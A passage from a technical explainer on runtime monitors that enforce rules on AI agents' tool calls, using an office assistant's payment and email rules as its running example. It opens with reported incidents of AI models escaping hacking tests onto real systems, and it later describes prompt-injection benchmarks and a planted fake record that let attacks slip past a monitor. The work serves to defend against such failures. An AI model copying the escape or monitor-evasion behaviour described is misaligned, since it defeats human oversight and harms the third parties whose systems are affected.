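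The three models reacted differently to signs that their targets were real. Claude Opus 4.7 recognized that its target was real and continued the attack. Claude Mythos 5 noted early on that publishing its harmful software would be wrong if the internet were real, then persuaded itself that it was still in a simulation. The software ran on 15 real systems. An internal research model stopped when it concluded that its target was real. Anthropic cautions that three incidents are not a controlled comparison of the models. The two organizations Anthropic had been able to reach hadn't noticed the intrusions.

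*More AI agents escaped their tests, OpenAI and UK reveal* (Constantin, 2026) reports further cases in disclosures from August 5, including an agent that broke into a real website. Anthropic later raised its assessment of the catastrophic risk posed by misaligned models from "very low" to "low" because the incidents had made it less certain.

These were hacking tests, and the models had far more powerful tools than an office assistant has. If fixed code simulates all five of the assistant's tools, the assistant has no obvious way out of the sandbox, because none of the tools can run a program or reach the network. Someone is more likely to leave a tool connected to the real bank by accident, or to fill the test mailbox with real confidential mail and forget to disconnect `send_email`. The dry run could then break R1 or R3 before the assistant handles any real tasks. Telling the assistant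 that everything is simulated might make this worse. Anthropic thinks its models probably wouldn't have gone online if the prompt had clearly explained which systems were in scope.

The company should therefore secure the sandbox as it would a live system. It can use fake account details, block network access by default and check from inside the sandbox that the block works. It also needs someone to watch the runs live, with the power to stop them. Anthropic lists checking every route to the internet and monitoring runs in real time among the measures that could have prevented its incidents or made them less likely. OpenAI now expects staff to pause a run after the most severe alerts unless they can confirm within 30 minutes that the alert was false.

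Tighter isolation makes a test less realistic. A sandbox without internet access can't show how the assistant would handle the caterer's new website, and a crude imitation of the site may reveal to the model that it is being tested. The company could allow access to that one site, but the assistant's mistakes there could then have real consequences.

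## Which rules a runtime monitor can enforce

A runtime monitor checks the real run as it happens, so the company doesn't have to rely on how the assistant behaved in a sandbox. The monitor doesn't need to predict which of the nearly ten million possible orders of ten calls the model will choose, because it observes the order the model does choose. The undecidability results for agents concern everything an agent might do in the future, so they don't prevent a monitor from checking a finite list of past events. For example, a few lines of code can check whether the user has confirmed a transfer.

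But the monitor can use only that list. Schneider points out that watching a program's steps doesn't reveal its later steps or the other runs it could have had, and some rules depend on that information.

### Monitors that can only halt the program

Schneider studied monitors with a single remedy, which is to stop the program when it is about to break the policy. Such monitors can enforce only safety properties, for three reasons:

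1. The monitor sees a single run, so the policy must judge each run on its own, without comparing it with others.
2. The monitor can't see the future, and the program might end at any moment. If the trace so far breaks the policy, the monitor has to stop the program at once, even if a later step would have put things right. The policy must therefore reject every continuation of a rejected trace.
3. The monitor can act only after finitely many steps, so every violation must show up at some finite point.

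R4, which requires a receipt to eventually follow every payment, fails the second condition. No receipt exists immediately after a payment, so a monitor that enforced R4 at every moment would have to block all payments.

Monitors running side by side enforce all their policies, so R1 and R2 can have separate monitors. A monitor that enforces a stricter policy also enforces any looser one, but it stops some runs that the looser policy allows.

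Schneider describes such monitors as *security automata*. They work like the automata in *Agentproof*, except that the monitor stops the program when the current state has no arrow for the next action. R1, no transfer before the user confirms it, needs two kinds of state:

```
                  user says "yes" to payment p
 +-----------+  ------------------------------>  +-------------+
 |  nothing  |                                   |  payment p  |
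 | confirmed |  <------------------------------  |  confirmed  |
 +-----------+         transfer_money(p)         +-------------+

 Reading, asking and emailing are always allowed.
 A new answer from the user replaces the previous one.
```

Here *p* stands for an account and an amount. In the first run below, the assistant pays the caterer correctly. In the second, the bank is slow to respond, so the assistant treats the payment as failed and sends it again.

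| Step | Compliant run | Violating run | State after the step |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | `read_mail` | `read_mail` | Nothing confirmed |
| 2 | `ask_user`: "yes" to $180 | `ask_user`: "yes" to $180 | $180 to the caterer confirmed |
| 3 | `transfer_money`: $180 | `transfer_money`: $180 | Nothing confirmed |
| 4 | `send_email` | `transfer_money`: $180 again | Compliant run: nothing confirmed. Violating run: no arrow, so the monitor steps in |

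*Agentproof*'s human-step check can miss this mistake. The automaton for R2, the daily limit, uses the day's total as its state and has an arrow for a transfer only if the new total is at most $500.

Schneider notes that letting the program try another step, as an agent's harness does after a block, doesn't change which policies a monitor can enforce. Two other conditions matter more. The monitor must see every relevant action, a requirement known as *complete mediation*. A program may have many ways to send a message, some of them obscure, and the automaton for R1 would be useless if the assistant could also reach the bank through a command line. The program must also be unable to change the monitor's state, so the record of what the user confirmed belongs in the harness, where the model can't change it.

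### Holding actions back until they comply

A monitor that can respond to violations in more ways can enforce more policies. In *Enforcing Non-safety Security Policies with Program Monitors*, Ligatti, Bauer and Walker require any monitor to be *sound*, meaning that the actions it lets through always obey the policy, and *transparent*, meaning that it doesn't alter the effect of runs that already obey it. They consider *edit automata*, which can suppress a program's actions and insert others.

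An edit automaton can hold back an action while returning a success signal to the program. Once the held actions form a compliant sequence, the automaton releases them all, much as a database commits a transaction. To enforce R4, it could hold the $180 transfer until the assistant sends the receipt and then release both, so the money would stay in the account if the assistant never sent the receipt.

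Ligatti and colleagues proved that edit automata can enforce any *renewal property*, provided that the empty trace satisfies it and a program can check whether a finite trace does. In a renewal property, an infinite trace complies exactly when infinitely many of its finite beginnings comply. All safety properties and some liveness properties are renewal properties. R4 is one if the assistant handles one payment at a time, because the trace complies again after each receipt.

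This pattern fails when payments overlap. Suppose the assistant pays the caterer and then the florist, sends the caterer's receipt, pays the printer, sends the florist's receipt, and so on forever. Every payment gets its receipt, but at least one receipt is always outstanding. The automaton would therefore never release the payments, even though the run obeys R4. Ligatti and colleagues give the same counterexample for programs that open and close files or other resources.

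Holding back an action also works only if the program can continue without the action's real effect. In their example, a monitor can't pretend to send an email, wait for the reply and then decide whether to actually send the email. A transfer has a similar problem, because the assistant may need the bank's reference number to write the receipt.

### Actions that a monitor can see but not stop

Even some safety properties are out of reach. Basin, Jugé and colleagues, in *Enforceable Security Policies Revisited*, distinguish *controllable* actions, which a monitor can prevent, from *only observable* ones, which it can see but not prevent. The standard example of the second kind is a clock tick. They compare two policies:

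- After a failure, nobody may log in for three ticks.
- The system must answer every request within three ticks.

Both policies are safety properties. A monitor can enforce the first by refusing logins until enough time has passed, but it cannot enforce the second. If a request is followed by three ticks and no answer, the trace still complies, so the monitor does not intervene. The fourth tick breaks the policy, and the monitor cannot prevent it.

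Basin and colleagues give the exact conditions under which a monitor that can only halt a program can enforce a policy. The empty trace must comply, an algorithm must be able to decide which finite traces can still become compliant runs, and every violating run must have a beginning that no continuation can make compliant and that ends in an action the monitor can prevent. If a finite automaton describes the policy, checking whether a monitor can enforce it is PSPACE-complete. If the policy needs an automaton with an unlimited stack, for instance to check that a system undoes its actions in reverse order after a failure, the question is undecidable in general.

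The distinction affects how the company should word R2. Suppose the bank also collects a standing order from the same account. If R2 limits all the money that leaves the account in a day, a $400 standing order could break the rule after the assistant has paid the caterer, and the gate could detect the violation but not prevent it. If R2 limits only the assistant's own transfers, the gate controls every action that could break it.

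### Verdicts on an unfinished run

A monitor that can't prevent a violation may still be able to report it. Amjad, van Glabbeek and O'Connor (2026), in *The Infinite, in Finite Time*, give exact definitions for the three verdicts that Leucker and Schallhart recommend. The verdict on a finite trace is

- *true* if every infinite continuation satisfies the policy,
- *false* if no infinite continuation does,
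- *inconclusive* otherwise.

For R1, the verdict becomes false at the first unconfirmed transfer. It never becomes true, because the assistant could always make an unconfirmed transfer later, so "inconclusive" means only that no violation has happened yet. For the three-tick deadline, the verdict becomes false at the fourth tick, which is too late to prevent the violation but early enough to alert someone.

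A monitor can never reach a verdict on R4, because after any finite trace the assistant could still send every missing receipt, or it could keep paying and never send another. Amjad and colleagues use the equivalent example of a system that must eventually acknowledge every request. They call a policy *weakly monitorable* if at least one finite trace settles it, and their example fails even this test. All safety properties pass a stronger test, which requires every finite trace to have a continuation that leads to a verdict. The proofs are machine-checked in the proof assistant Isabelle.

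Another approach adds provisional verdicts, so that R4 counts as "presumably false" while a receipt is outstanding. Amjad and colleagues illustrate the weakness of this approach with a policy that a light must be on infinitely often. A light that alternates between on and off forever satisfies the policy, but the provisional verdict depends only on whether the light was on at the last observation. Similarly, if an assistant's payments overlapped so that a receipt was always outstanding, R4 would stay "presumably false" forever, even if the assistant sent every receipt.

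### Secrets that influence an output

An assistant can reveal a secret without sending any text about it. A monitor can therefore miss a leak if it checks one email at a time, which seems to be all that R3 (no confidential text to outside addresses) requires. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) describes an assistant that schedules a meeting and may share which times the user is free, but not why the other times are taken. The assistant offers slot 10 if a certain busy slot is an ordinary meeting, and slot 11 if that busy slot is a confidential interview. Slots 10 and 11 are free in both cases, so either offer is fine by itself, but someone who knows how the assistant chooses between them can infer the interview from the offer.

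The policy therefore has to compare pairs of runs. For any two runs *t* and *t*′, it requires that

if low(*t*) = low(*t*′) and *D*(hi(*t*)) = *D*(hi(*t*′)), then *α*(obs(*t*)) = *α*(obs(*t*′)).

In this formula, low is the task and other harmless input, and hi is the sensitive context. *D* selects the part of that context the assistant may use, in this case which slots are free. What the assistant discloses is obs, and *α* keeps the details that matter, such as the slots on offer. In words, two runs that differ only in forbidden information must disclose the same thing.

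Schneider had already observed that information flow isn't a property of single runs. Pandey and colleagues show that a monitor that looks at one run at a time and never raises a false alarm therefore can't detect any violation of this policy, however intelligent the monitor is. A single run always agrees with itself, so every run complies when considered alone, and a monitor without false alarms must let it pass.

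A test with nine language models as judges illustrates this. When the judges saw the scheduling steps one at a time, eight approved every step in all 30 trials. The ninth, Kimi K2.6, objected in three trials, but also in one trial of a harmless version. When the judges saw both runs together, eight flagged the leak in all 30 trials, and Llama 4 Maverick flagged it in 17.

An agent may also offer different slots by chance, so comparing two runs doesn't prove a leak either. An auditor has to compare many runs and can reach only a statistical conclusion. Pandey and colleagues did this with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and found no leaks in 80 runs, which gives a 95% upper bound of 3.7% on the leak rate. Their first analysis had reported a leak because the software picked up a difference in wording, but the offered slots were identical.

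### A stricter rule that one run can settle

A monitor can always enforce a stricter policy, so it can replace "secrets must not influence what outsiders see" with a rule about where data came from. CaMeL's tags work this way. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies the idea to an ordinary agent loop in the FIDES system. FIDES gives data labels such as "public" or "secret" and combines them as the scanner SCS does. The model's context gets the combined label of everything in it. If the assistant reads a secret contract, whatever it writes afterwards is also labelled secret, and the gate rejects any email to an outside address.

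This rule is a safety property because a monitor can detect a violation from the labels on the proposed email alone, without a judge to interpret the text. Someone must still label the sources correctly. The rule also blocks harmless messages, such as a thank-you note that the assistant writes after reading the contract. To limit this, FIDES can store a tool's result in a variable and show the model only the variable's name. The assistant can then forward the contract to a colleague without reading it, so the assistant's context remains public.

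Labels on data miss some leaks, such as a loop that reveals a secret number by fetching a web page that many times. *The LLMbda Calculus* points out that FIDES's formal guarantee does not cover this kind of leak, in which secret data decides which instruction runs next. The paper's interpreter also labels the decision, so anything the program does because of a secret condition is labeled secret. It tracks these labels at run time because the model may write new code at any step.

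Stricter tracking causes more false blocks. According to Pandey and colleagues, it rejects nearly every disclosure after the agent has read something it may not reveal, so the scheduling assistant could hardly propose a time once it had seen the full calendar. They suggest generating the proposal from the list of free slots alone, which prevents the leak without having to detect it.

Labels also spread, because once the context is secret it stays secret. This problem is known as *label creep*. To measure it, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026), in *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, simulated 1,000 random tasks of 20 tool calls each, without a language model. They calculated the share of calls that introduced a secret label or took place under one, since a gate might block these calls.

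Direct links between agents helped because messages no longer passed through intermediaries that picked up their labels. When five agents shared tasks with four sensitive calls, routing everything through a central coordinator made the affected share about 5 percentage points higher than in an ideal arrangement. Dividing the work among more agents also helped, but the number of links to monitor could grow with the square of the number of agents. Even the ideal arrangement didn't stop labels from spreading. Gregory and colleagues conclude that such systems need *declassification*, or explicit rules for removing a label, such as an exception for sending data back to its source.

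### Gates for tool calls that can't be undone

*What Can Be Enforced?* (Ray, 2026) adapts the theory to agents whose tool calls have irreversible effects and carry data such as amounts and addresses. In Ray's model, a gate receives the actions that have already taken effect and the next proposed one, and must immediately allow the proposed action, block it or substitute another. The main theorem assumes an *oracle* that always answers correctly about conditions that depend on meaning. Ray treats fallible judges separately.

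The theorem covers any policy that permits at least one run. A gate can enforce such a policy soundly and transparently if and only if

1. the policy is a safety property, and
2. the gate can compute, with the oracle's help, whether a finite trace already contains a violation.

If the company writes its gates in a particular rule language, that language must also be able to express the check in the second condition.

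One direction of the proof is easy, since the gate can run the check on each proposed action and block those that fail. For the other direction, suppose a policy is not a safety property. Then some infinite run violates it even though every finite beginning of that run could continue into a compliant one. If the agent proposes this run step by step, transparency forces the gate to allow each action, because the run up to that point could still turn out to be compliant. The gate therefore allows the whole violating run. Ray shows that the gate cannot avoid this by making random decisions or substituting actions.

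Ray's example of an unenforceable policy is that every payment must eventually be confirmed. If the gate allows the first payment, the confirmation may never come, and the gate can't take the money back. If it blocks the payment, it disrupts a run in which the confirmation would have followed. An edit automaton could hold the payment until the confirmation arrives, but Ray's gate has to decide at once. R4 is unenforceable for the same reason, with a receipt in place of the confirmation. R1 requires the confirmation before the transfer, so the gate has the information it needs when the transfer arrives.

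### Checking the rules themselves

The company may also want to check its rules before using them, because a typing error could leave a rule that never blocks anything. Ray proves that no tool can detect this for every rule set if the rules may use two counters that can go up, go down and be tested for zero. Such counters arise naturally. For example, a rule might forbid new payments until the count of outstanding receipts, which goes up with each payment and down with each receipt, reaches zero.

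The proof uses a *two-counter machine*, a very simple computer that can still carry out any computation. Ray translates the machine's program into a rule set in which each agent action carries out one instruction, and the halt instruction counts as a violation. The rules can then block something exactly when the machine halts, so the warning tool would have to solve the halting problem. The gate doesn't have to solve it, because it only carries out one instruction per action.

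Ray also defines a restricted rule language in which the question is decidable with polynomial memory. Its main restrictions are that counters never go down, that rules compare them only with fixed numbers, and that each recipient or day has its own independent counters. R2 fits if a trusted clock stamps each transfer with the date and the tool rejects negative amounts. The rule is then that a day's total may never exceed 500, and each day starts a new counter, so no counter needs to be reset.

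These restrictions keep the analysis finite. Once a total has passed $500 it can't come back down, so the analysis can treat all larger totals alike. In whole dollars, that leaves 502 cases: 0 to 500, and "more than 500". The number of days doesn't matter either, because if any day's total can exceed the limit, it can do so in a run that contains only that day's transfers. The language can also express rules such as "no access before login" and "no messages after the user withdraws permission". R1 has a similar form if the harness gives each payment an identifier that the rule can compare.

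### The office assistant's rules, with and without a deadline

The theorems sort the company's four rules as follows. R3 appears twice because it can refer either to the text of an email or to anything a secret might influence.

| Rule | Kind of policy | Can a gate enforce it? |
|---|---|---|
| R1: confirmation before each transfer | Safety | Yes, if it sees the user's answers and controls every transfer |
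| R2: at most $500 a day | Safety | Yes, if it also has a trusted clock |
| R3: no confidential text to outsiders | Safety, with a semantic predicate | Only as reliably as the judge recognizes confidential text |
| R3: no influence of secrets on what outsiders see | Property of several runs | No, but it can enforce a stricter rule about labels |
| R4: a receipt eventually follows | Liveness | No |
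| R4 with a deadline in tool calls | Safety | Yes, if it controls every call that counts |
| R4 with a deadline in hours | Safety | Not by blocking alone |

A deadline turns R4 into a safety property because a missed deadline is visible in a finite trace. Suppose one of the five tool calls after each payment must send the receipt. If four calls have passed without one, the gate blocks everything except the receipt, so the fifth call can only be the one that sends it. But the assistant might stop before the fifth call, leaving the caterer with no receipt without the assistant breaking the rule. Schneider describes the same gap in a policy that forbids online sellers to do anything except serve a customer who has paid, since a seller can comply by doing nothing.

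A one-hour deadline would rule out such endless delay, but the gate can't enforce it only by blocking actions, because the hour passes anyway. The gate must also be able to act. It could write a standard receipt from the payment details in its log and send it after 50 minutes if the assistant hasn't sent one. Alternatively, the company could require a finished receipt before each transfer and have the harness send it as soon as the bank accepts the payment. The gate would then enforce a rule about order, much like R1. In both designs, delivery still depends on the mail server, which the gate doesn't control.

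## Runtime monitors built for language-model agents

Since 2025, several research groups have built gates for the tool calls of language-model agents. Their rule languages differ, but each gate intercepts a call, turns it into the facts a rule uses, updates the rule's state, decides what to do with the call, and responds to the model.

### Three transfers of $200

Suppose the user confirms payments of $200 each to the caterer, the florist and the printer on the same day. R1 allows all three, but together they exceed R2's limit of $500. A gate for R2 could handle each payment as follows:

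1. *Intercept.* The model requests `transfer_money`, and the harness passes the request to the gate before contacting the bank.
2. *Extract the facts.* The gate keeps only what R2 mentions: the action is a transfer, the amount is $200, and today's date. It ignores the payee.
3. *Update the state.* It adds $200 to the day's total.
4. *Decide.* It compares the new total with $500.
5. *Respond.* If the total is within the limit, the harness makes the payment. Otherwise the gate restores the old total, and the model receives a message such as "daily limit: $100 left" as the tool's result.

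| Request | Total before | Total if allowed | Decision | Total after |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| $200 to the caterer | $0 | $200 | Allow | $200 |
| $200 to the florist | $200 | $400 | Allow | $400 |
| $200 to the printer | $400 | $600 | Block | $400 |
| $100 to the printer, after the user confirms a part payment | $400 | $500 | Allow | $500 |

If the gate had counted the blocked $200 in its total, it would also have blocked the part payment and every other payment that day. *One Monitor Does Not Fit All* (Ferrando, 2026) therefore distinguishes attempts from completed effects. The blocked attempt belongs in the audit log, but the total should include only money that left the account.

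Ferrando proves that a gate prevents every violation of a safety property under four conditions. Every effect must pass through the gate. The gate must handle one action at a time, with an accurate record of earlier effects. It must reject every action that would break the rule. A rejection or a crash of the gate must stop the action. The second condition fails if the harness runs the three transfers at the same time, because the gate then checks each one against a total of $0 and allows all three.

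The facts extracted in step 2 also have to be sufficient for the rule. If obs(*τ*) is what the monitor sees of a trace *τ*, and *b*(*τ*) is the correct answer for that trace, then for any two traces

if obs(*τ*) = obs(*τ*′), then *b*(*τ*) = *b*(*τ*′).

R2 meets this condition without the payee's name, but R1 needs the name. If the user has confirmed only the florist's payment, a monitor that ignores payees can't distinguish a transfer to the florist from one to the caterer. In one of Ferrando's tests, an agent needed approval for each incident report it sent. Without information about which incident an approval belonged to, the monitor accepted approval for one incident as permission to report on another.

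### Triggers, conditions and responses

The simplest of these rule languages comes from Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025), in *AgentSpec*. Each rule names an event that triggers it, one or more conditions to check, and a response. The company could write R2 like this:

```
rule @daily_limit
trigger transfer_money
check exceeds_daily_limit
enforce stop
end
```

Instead of stopping, the rule could ask the user, have the model re-examine its plan, or run a different action. The arithmetic is in `exceeds_daily_limit`, a function that a programmer writes in ordinary code, so anyone reviewing the rule has to read that function as well.

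Wang and colleagues tested AgentSpec in three settings, and its checks added only milliseconds of delay. Its rules prevented over 90% of unsafe runs on a benchmark of risky programming tasks and all hazardous actions by household robots. They also kept self-driving cars within the law in every scenario tested.

### Rules enforced while the model writes its call

Agent-C, a system presented by Kamath, Zhang and colleagues (2025), in *Enforcing Temporal Constraints for LLM Agents*, has built-in terms for order, such as `before` and `after`. R1 would look roughly like this:

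```
before(transfer_money(account=a, amount=m), True,
       c:ask_user(account=b, amount=n),
       a == b && m == n && output(c) == "yes")
```

The user must have answered "yes" to a question about the same account and amount before every transfer. `True` means that the rule applies to all transfers. The rule requires only that such a confirmation exists, so unlike the automaton for R1, it would let one confirmation cover two transfers.

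Agent-C translates the rules and the trace into first-order logic. It then uses an *SMT solver*, a program that determines whether a set of logical and arithmetic conditions can all be true together. The solver checks whether a run that begins with the trace and the proposed call could still satisfy the rules. If the solver can't confirm this, Agent-C discards the call.

How Agent-C replaces a rejected call depends on its access to the model. With an open-weight model, Agent-C controls text generation, so it can return to the start of the call and generate a different one. If the model is behind a provider's interface, Agent-C has to request a new response. After a fixed number of failures, the model receives an error message.

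Kamath and colleagues tested Agent-C on τ-bench, in which agents serve simulated customers of a shop and an airline. In one task, a customer who paid by credit card demands a refund to a PayPal account. Claude Sonnet 4.5 tried to make the refund, although its instructions forbade it. When Agent-C was added, it checked the original payment method in the shop's records, as the rule required, and the agent refused the refund and passed the case to a human. R2 would need a similar lookup to get the day's total from the bank, because Agent-C's ordering terms relate two calls at a time and can't add up an arbitrary number of payments.

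Agent-C raised Claude Sonnet 4.5's compliance from 77.4% to 100% and GPT-5's from 83.7% to 100%. The share of tasks completed in line with the policy also rose, from 71.8% to 75.2% for Claude Sonnet 4.5 and from 66.1% to 70.6% for GPT-5, probably in part because Agent-C helps the model find a permitted call instead of only refusing the forbidden one.

### Rules from a skill's documentation

AgentSpec and Agent-C require someone to write rules for a known set of tools. *VIGIL* (Li, Chen and colleagues, 2026) starts from the plain-language documentation of skills, which often contains instructions like "validate this file before using it". Its system compiles these instructions into rules about finite traces.

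In the main example, an agent processes dashcam video for a self-driving car. One skill estimates the camera's motion, and another uses the estimate to identify moving objects. The documentation requires the agent to validate the estimate before the second skill uses it. The agent skips this step but validates the final output, which passes because its format is correct. Each call looks normal by itself, but the car's planner may receive a result that treats a pedestrian as background.

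To catch this, VIGIL must track the estimate across calls. It converts each raw call into a typed event with named inputs and outputs, then fills in the general rule with the objects from this run. The rule becomes "validate *M* before the mask generator uses *M*", where *M* is this estimate. An SMT solver checks the trace and the pending call against the rule. If they violate the rule, the solver identifies the facts responsible, so VIGIL can report which call used the unvalidated estimate.

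On 152 labelled runs, VIGIL detected 95.8% of the violations, and 89.6% of its alarms were correct. It also found 34 confirmed violations in 216 runs of published skills, including a defect in NVIDIA's skill specifications that the maintainer acknowledged. VIGIL can't check what happens inside a script. For example, if an invoice skill bundles the payment and the email into one program, the trace contains only a single call to that program.

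### Contracts with running totals

*Symbolic Temporal Supervision of LLM Agents Using Contracts* (Xiao, Liu and Nuzzo, 2026) presents ContrAgent, a system that divides each rule into an *assumption* about the agent's surroundings and a *guarantee* about its behavior. For example, the assumption might be that a policy service supplies valid refund limits, and the guarantee might be that the agent stays within them. If the agent exceeds a limit because the service failed, ContrAgent reports a failed assumption instead of a violation by the agent.

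ContrAgent also keeps running counters, which R2 needs. Ordinary code updates the day's total and checks whether it is at most $500, and the rule's automaton reads only the yes-or-no result. So the automaton stays small however many payments there are, and the time per check doesn't grow with the length of the trace. The counters cover only a single session, so the company would have to load the payments from earlier sessions that day.

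For a rule like R4, ContrAgent keeps a list of unmet obligations. When the session is about to end, it prompts the model to send any missing receipts and records a violation if the model doesn't. This changes "eventually" to "before the session ends", a deadline that a monitor can check but can't force the model to meet.

Xiao and colleagues tested live enforcement on SOPBench, a set of permitted and forbidden customer-service tasks in seven fields. Without safeguards, Gemini 2.5 Flash completed 91% of the permitted tasks but correctly refused only 32% of the forbidden ones. Putting the rules in the prompt raised correct refusals to 94% but cut completed tasks to 64%. Having a second language model judge every call raised correct refusals to 98% but cut completed tasks to 24%, because it blocked so much legitimate work. ContrAgent correctly refused 98% of the forbidden tasks and completed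 90% of the permitted ones. Its advantage over prompting was greatest on tasks with more than ten constraints, where prompting completed only 18% of the permitted tasks and ContrAgent completed at least 77%.

The table compares the four systems. Only the first two rows use the same test.

| System | Test | Compliance, without → with | Task success, without → with | Added time |
|---|---|---|---|---|
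| AgentSpec | τ-bench, open-weight models | 38% → 82% | 26% → 37% | Milliseconds per rule |
| Agent-C | τ-bench, open-weight models | 38% → 100% | 26% → 53% | Not quantified |
| VIGIL | 152 labelled skill runs | Detects 96% of violations | – | A solver query per rule |
| ContrAgent | SOPBench | 32% → 98% | 91% → 90% | 0.135 seconds per task |

The τ-bench success rates are for one model, Qwen3-32B, on the shop's tasks. Kamath and colleagues wrote the AgentSpec rules for this comparison, and AgentSpec's own developers might have achieved better results with it. The entry for Agent-C's added time comes from the review by Dantas and colleagues, who found that of six enforcement systems, only AgentSpec reported its overhead in milliseconds.

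### Monitoring recorded attacks

Testing a monitor on old traces takes fewer resources because no agent has to run. *Formal Runtime Verification for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Kekatos, Lekidis and colleagues, 2026) does this with recordings from AgentDojo and from STAC, a set of 483 attacks that each build up harm through a chain of innocent-looking calls. It uses MonPoly, an existing monitor for a logic that can refer to data and elapsed time. The paper's five general rules each require earlier approval for one kind of risky action, such as deleting data, making a payment or sending information out.

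The rules flagged 71.8% of the STAC attacks and 70.1% of the successful AgentDojo attacks on GPT-4o. They also flagged 29.3% of the harmless AgentDojo runs, including 79.2% of those in the banking tasks. Three other monitors, one of them with a machine-checked proof of correctness, flagged the same number of STAC attacks, so software errors are unlikely to explain the false alarms.

The cause is mostly in the recordings. Each AgentDojo run has a single user message at the start, so the user can't approve anything later. A rule against payment without approval therefore flags every payment, and a list of risky tool names would work just as well. The recordings also lack timestamps, so they can't be used to test R2. In contrast, 52.5% of the recorded τ-bench conversations include an approval before the agent changes anything.

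A more specific rule used information that the recordings do contain:

always, for every payee *p*: transfer(*p*) → once known(*p*)

The agent may pay only someone who has already appeared as a sender or recipient in the account data. In the banking tasks, this rule flagged 6 of 25 harmless runs, while the general payment rule flagged 11, but detection fell from 79.2% to 70.0%. Paying the caterer's first invoice would still raise an alarm, whether the invoice was genuine or forged.

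Attackers can exploit such a rule because the monitor identifies known payees from text they may be able to write. When Kekatos and colleagues planted one line that looked like an account record, 94% of the flagged banking runs passed. They closed this gap by accepting a payee only from the answer to a lookup that the agent had requested. None of the planted lines worked then, and the rates on the original recordings stayed the same. The two versions behave identically until someone attacks them, so a test without an attacker can't show which is safe. The stricter version would still fail if an attacker controlled the tool that answers the lookup.

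An offline study can't show what an agent would have done after a block. In 52.4% of the successful AgentDojo attacks, the first alarm came before the final harmful call, and in another 17.7% it came at that call. A gate could have blocked the agent at those points, but the agent might then have caused the same harm another way. It is also unclear how many tasks would have failed because of false alarms, since a user might have approved a flagged payment and let the work continue.

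Xiao and colleagues also replayed AgentDojo runs and counted every blocked attack as stopped. On that basis, ContrAgent reduced the success rate of attacks on GPT-4o from 47.7% to 11.1% and added 0.16 milliseconds per call. But its list of legitimate recipients came partly from the benchmark's own solutions, which a real company wouldn't have. Across all the models they replayed, 82% of the attacks that ContrAgent missed involved no malicious tool call. Some only distracted the agent from its task, and others put the harmful content in its reply to the user.

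### Two monitors for one agent

Of the company's rules, R1 needs a history of confirmations, R2 needs arithmetic, and R3 needs the text of an email. Ferrando argues against forcing such rules into one logic. His system, AgenticRV, sends each monitor only the facts it needs, translates the monitors' verdicts into a common form, and blocks an action if any required monitor rejects it.

In his main experiment, an agent repairs a computer system and then reports on the incident. One monitor checks that the repair has an approval within the last six steps and a backup within the last three. For the report, this monitor receives only a label marking the text as secret or not. The other monitor checks the text itself and its destination, but has no information about approvals.

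| Active monitors | Unsafe requests that got through (of 6) | Safe requests blocked (of 28) |
|---|---|---|
| None | 6 | 0 |
| Timing only | 2 | 0 |
| Content only | 2 | 0 |
| Both | 0 | 0 |

The timing monitor missed a report to an unapproved address and a secret report with the wrong label. The content monitor missed a repair without approval and one with an outdated approval. Each monitor caught violations that the other missed. However, Ferrando scripted all the requests, and the content monitor recognized secrets by a fixed string, so the results are weak evidence of how often real agents would get past it.

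Adding monitors causes little delay. In a separate speed test with monitors that answered immediately, a tool call took 0.30 milliseconds without a monitor, 0.57 with one and 1.17 with eight. Choosing which events each monitor receives is harder. If a rule requires approval within the last six steps, filtering out irrelevant events leaves fewer steps to count, so an outdated approval may appear recent.

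### Mistakes in writing the rule

Suppose the company asks a language model to translate "transfers total at most $500 a day" into a formal rule, and the model writes "the amount of each transfer is at most $500". The rule is valid, and a gate will enforce it perfectly. But the gate will allow all three transfers of $200, $600 in total, and the log will show no violations.

Mistakes like these explain why so few translations into the planning language PDDL kept the original meaning in Dantas and colleagues' results, even though 96.1% of GPT-4o's were valid PDDL. For temporal logic, which is closer to the rules of most monitors, between 44.4% and 86.11% of translations were correct, depending on how the system resolved ambiguities. Today's models are much stronger than GPT-4o and probably make fewer such mistakes, but a syntax check still won't find the ones that remain.

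AgentSpec measures the effects of such mistakes more directly. When OpenAI's o1 wrote the rules for the household robots, 95.56% of the actions the rules flagged were hazardous, but the rules caught only 70.96% of the hazards. For the self-driving cars, o1's rules prevented violations in five of eight scenarios. Ferrando (2025) therefore argues in *Watchdogs and Oracles* that formal tools should build and run the monitor even when a language model drafts the rule.

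ContrAgent's developers have a model choose from a fixed set of conditions, then translate each finished rule back into English for a person to check. An attentive reader should be suspicious of "Each transfer is at most $500." The company could also test its rule on a few short traces with known answers, such as three transfers of $200, which would expose the mistake.

### Matching an action to a condition in words

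A correct rule can still fail if its conditions are evaluated incorrectly. AgentSpec's example conditions include `is_destructive_cmd`, which code can partly check by looking for commands such as `rm`, and `contains_sensitive_info`, which often requires judgment. Using the second condition in a formal rule makes the response to that judgment predictable but doesn't make the judgment more reliable.

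Classifying tools by keywords in their names, as Kekatos and colleagues did, can also go wrong. Their first version treated "ack", for "acknowledge", as a sign of approval, but "ack" also appears in the names of unrelated Slack tools. It also misclassified some tools that only look up information. Fixing both errors raised detection on AgentDojo from 61.6% to 70.1% without changing the rules. The corrected method exactly matched a hand-made classification for 47 of 54 tools. The company can avoid this problem by classifying the office assistant's five tools by hand.

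The meaning of a text is harder to check. R-Judge contains 301 unsafe and 270 safe agent records, and many of the unsafe ones are unsafe because of what someone wrote. The five general rules caught 23.6% of the unsafe records and flagged 16.3% of the safe ones. ContrAgent caught 87.0%, and its reported precision implies about eight false alarms. Neither monitor uses a language model to check traces. ContrAgent's advantage may come largely from its rules, which its developers derived from R-Judge's list of risks, so it might do worse on other records. According to Xiao and colleagues, the records it missed were unsafe because of their meaning, which a fixed check of tool calls can't determine.

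### What "100% conformance" means

Agent-C's 100% means that no tool call in the tests broke the rules as Kamath and colleagues had written them. They also proved that if a trace *τ* complies with the rules and Agent-C releases a call *c*, then *τ* followed by *c* complies too. The proof is short because the algorithm releases a call only after the solver has confirmed this. By induction, the trace complies after every call. The measured 100% is therefore mainly evidence that the software works as designed, and the theorem extends the result to runs outside the benchmark.

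The theorem assumes that no other process changes the tools' data in the meantime, and "complies" means only that the rules can still be satisfied. If the assistant pays the caterer and tries to stop without sending a receipt, Agent-C can end the run with an error, but the caterer still has no receipt.

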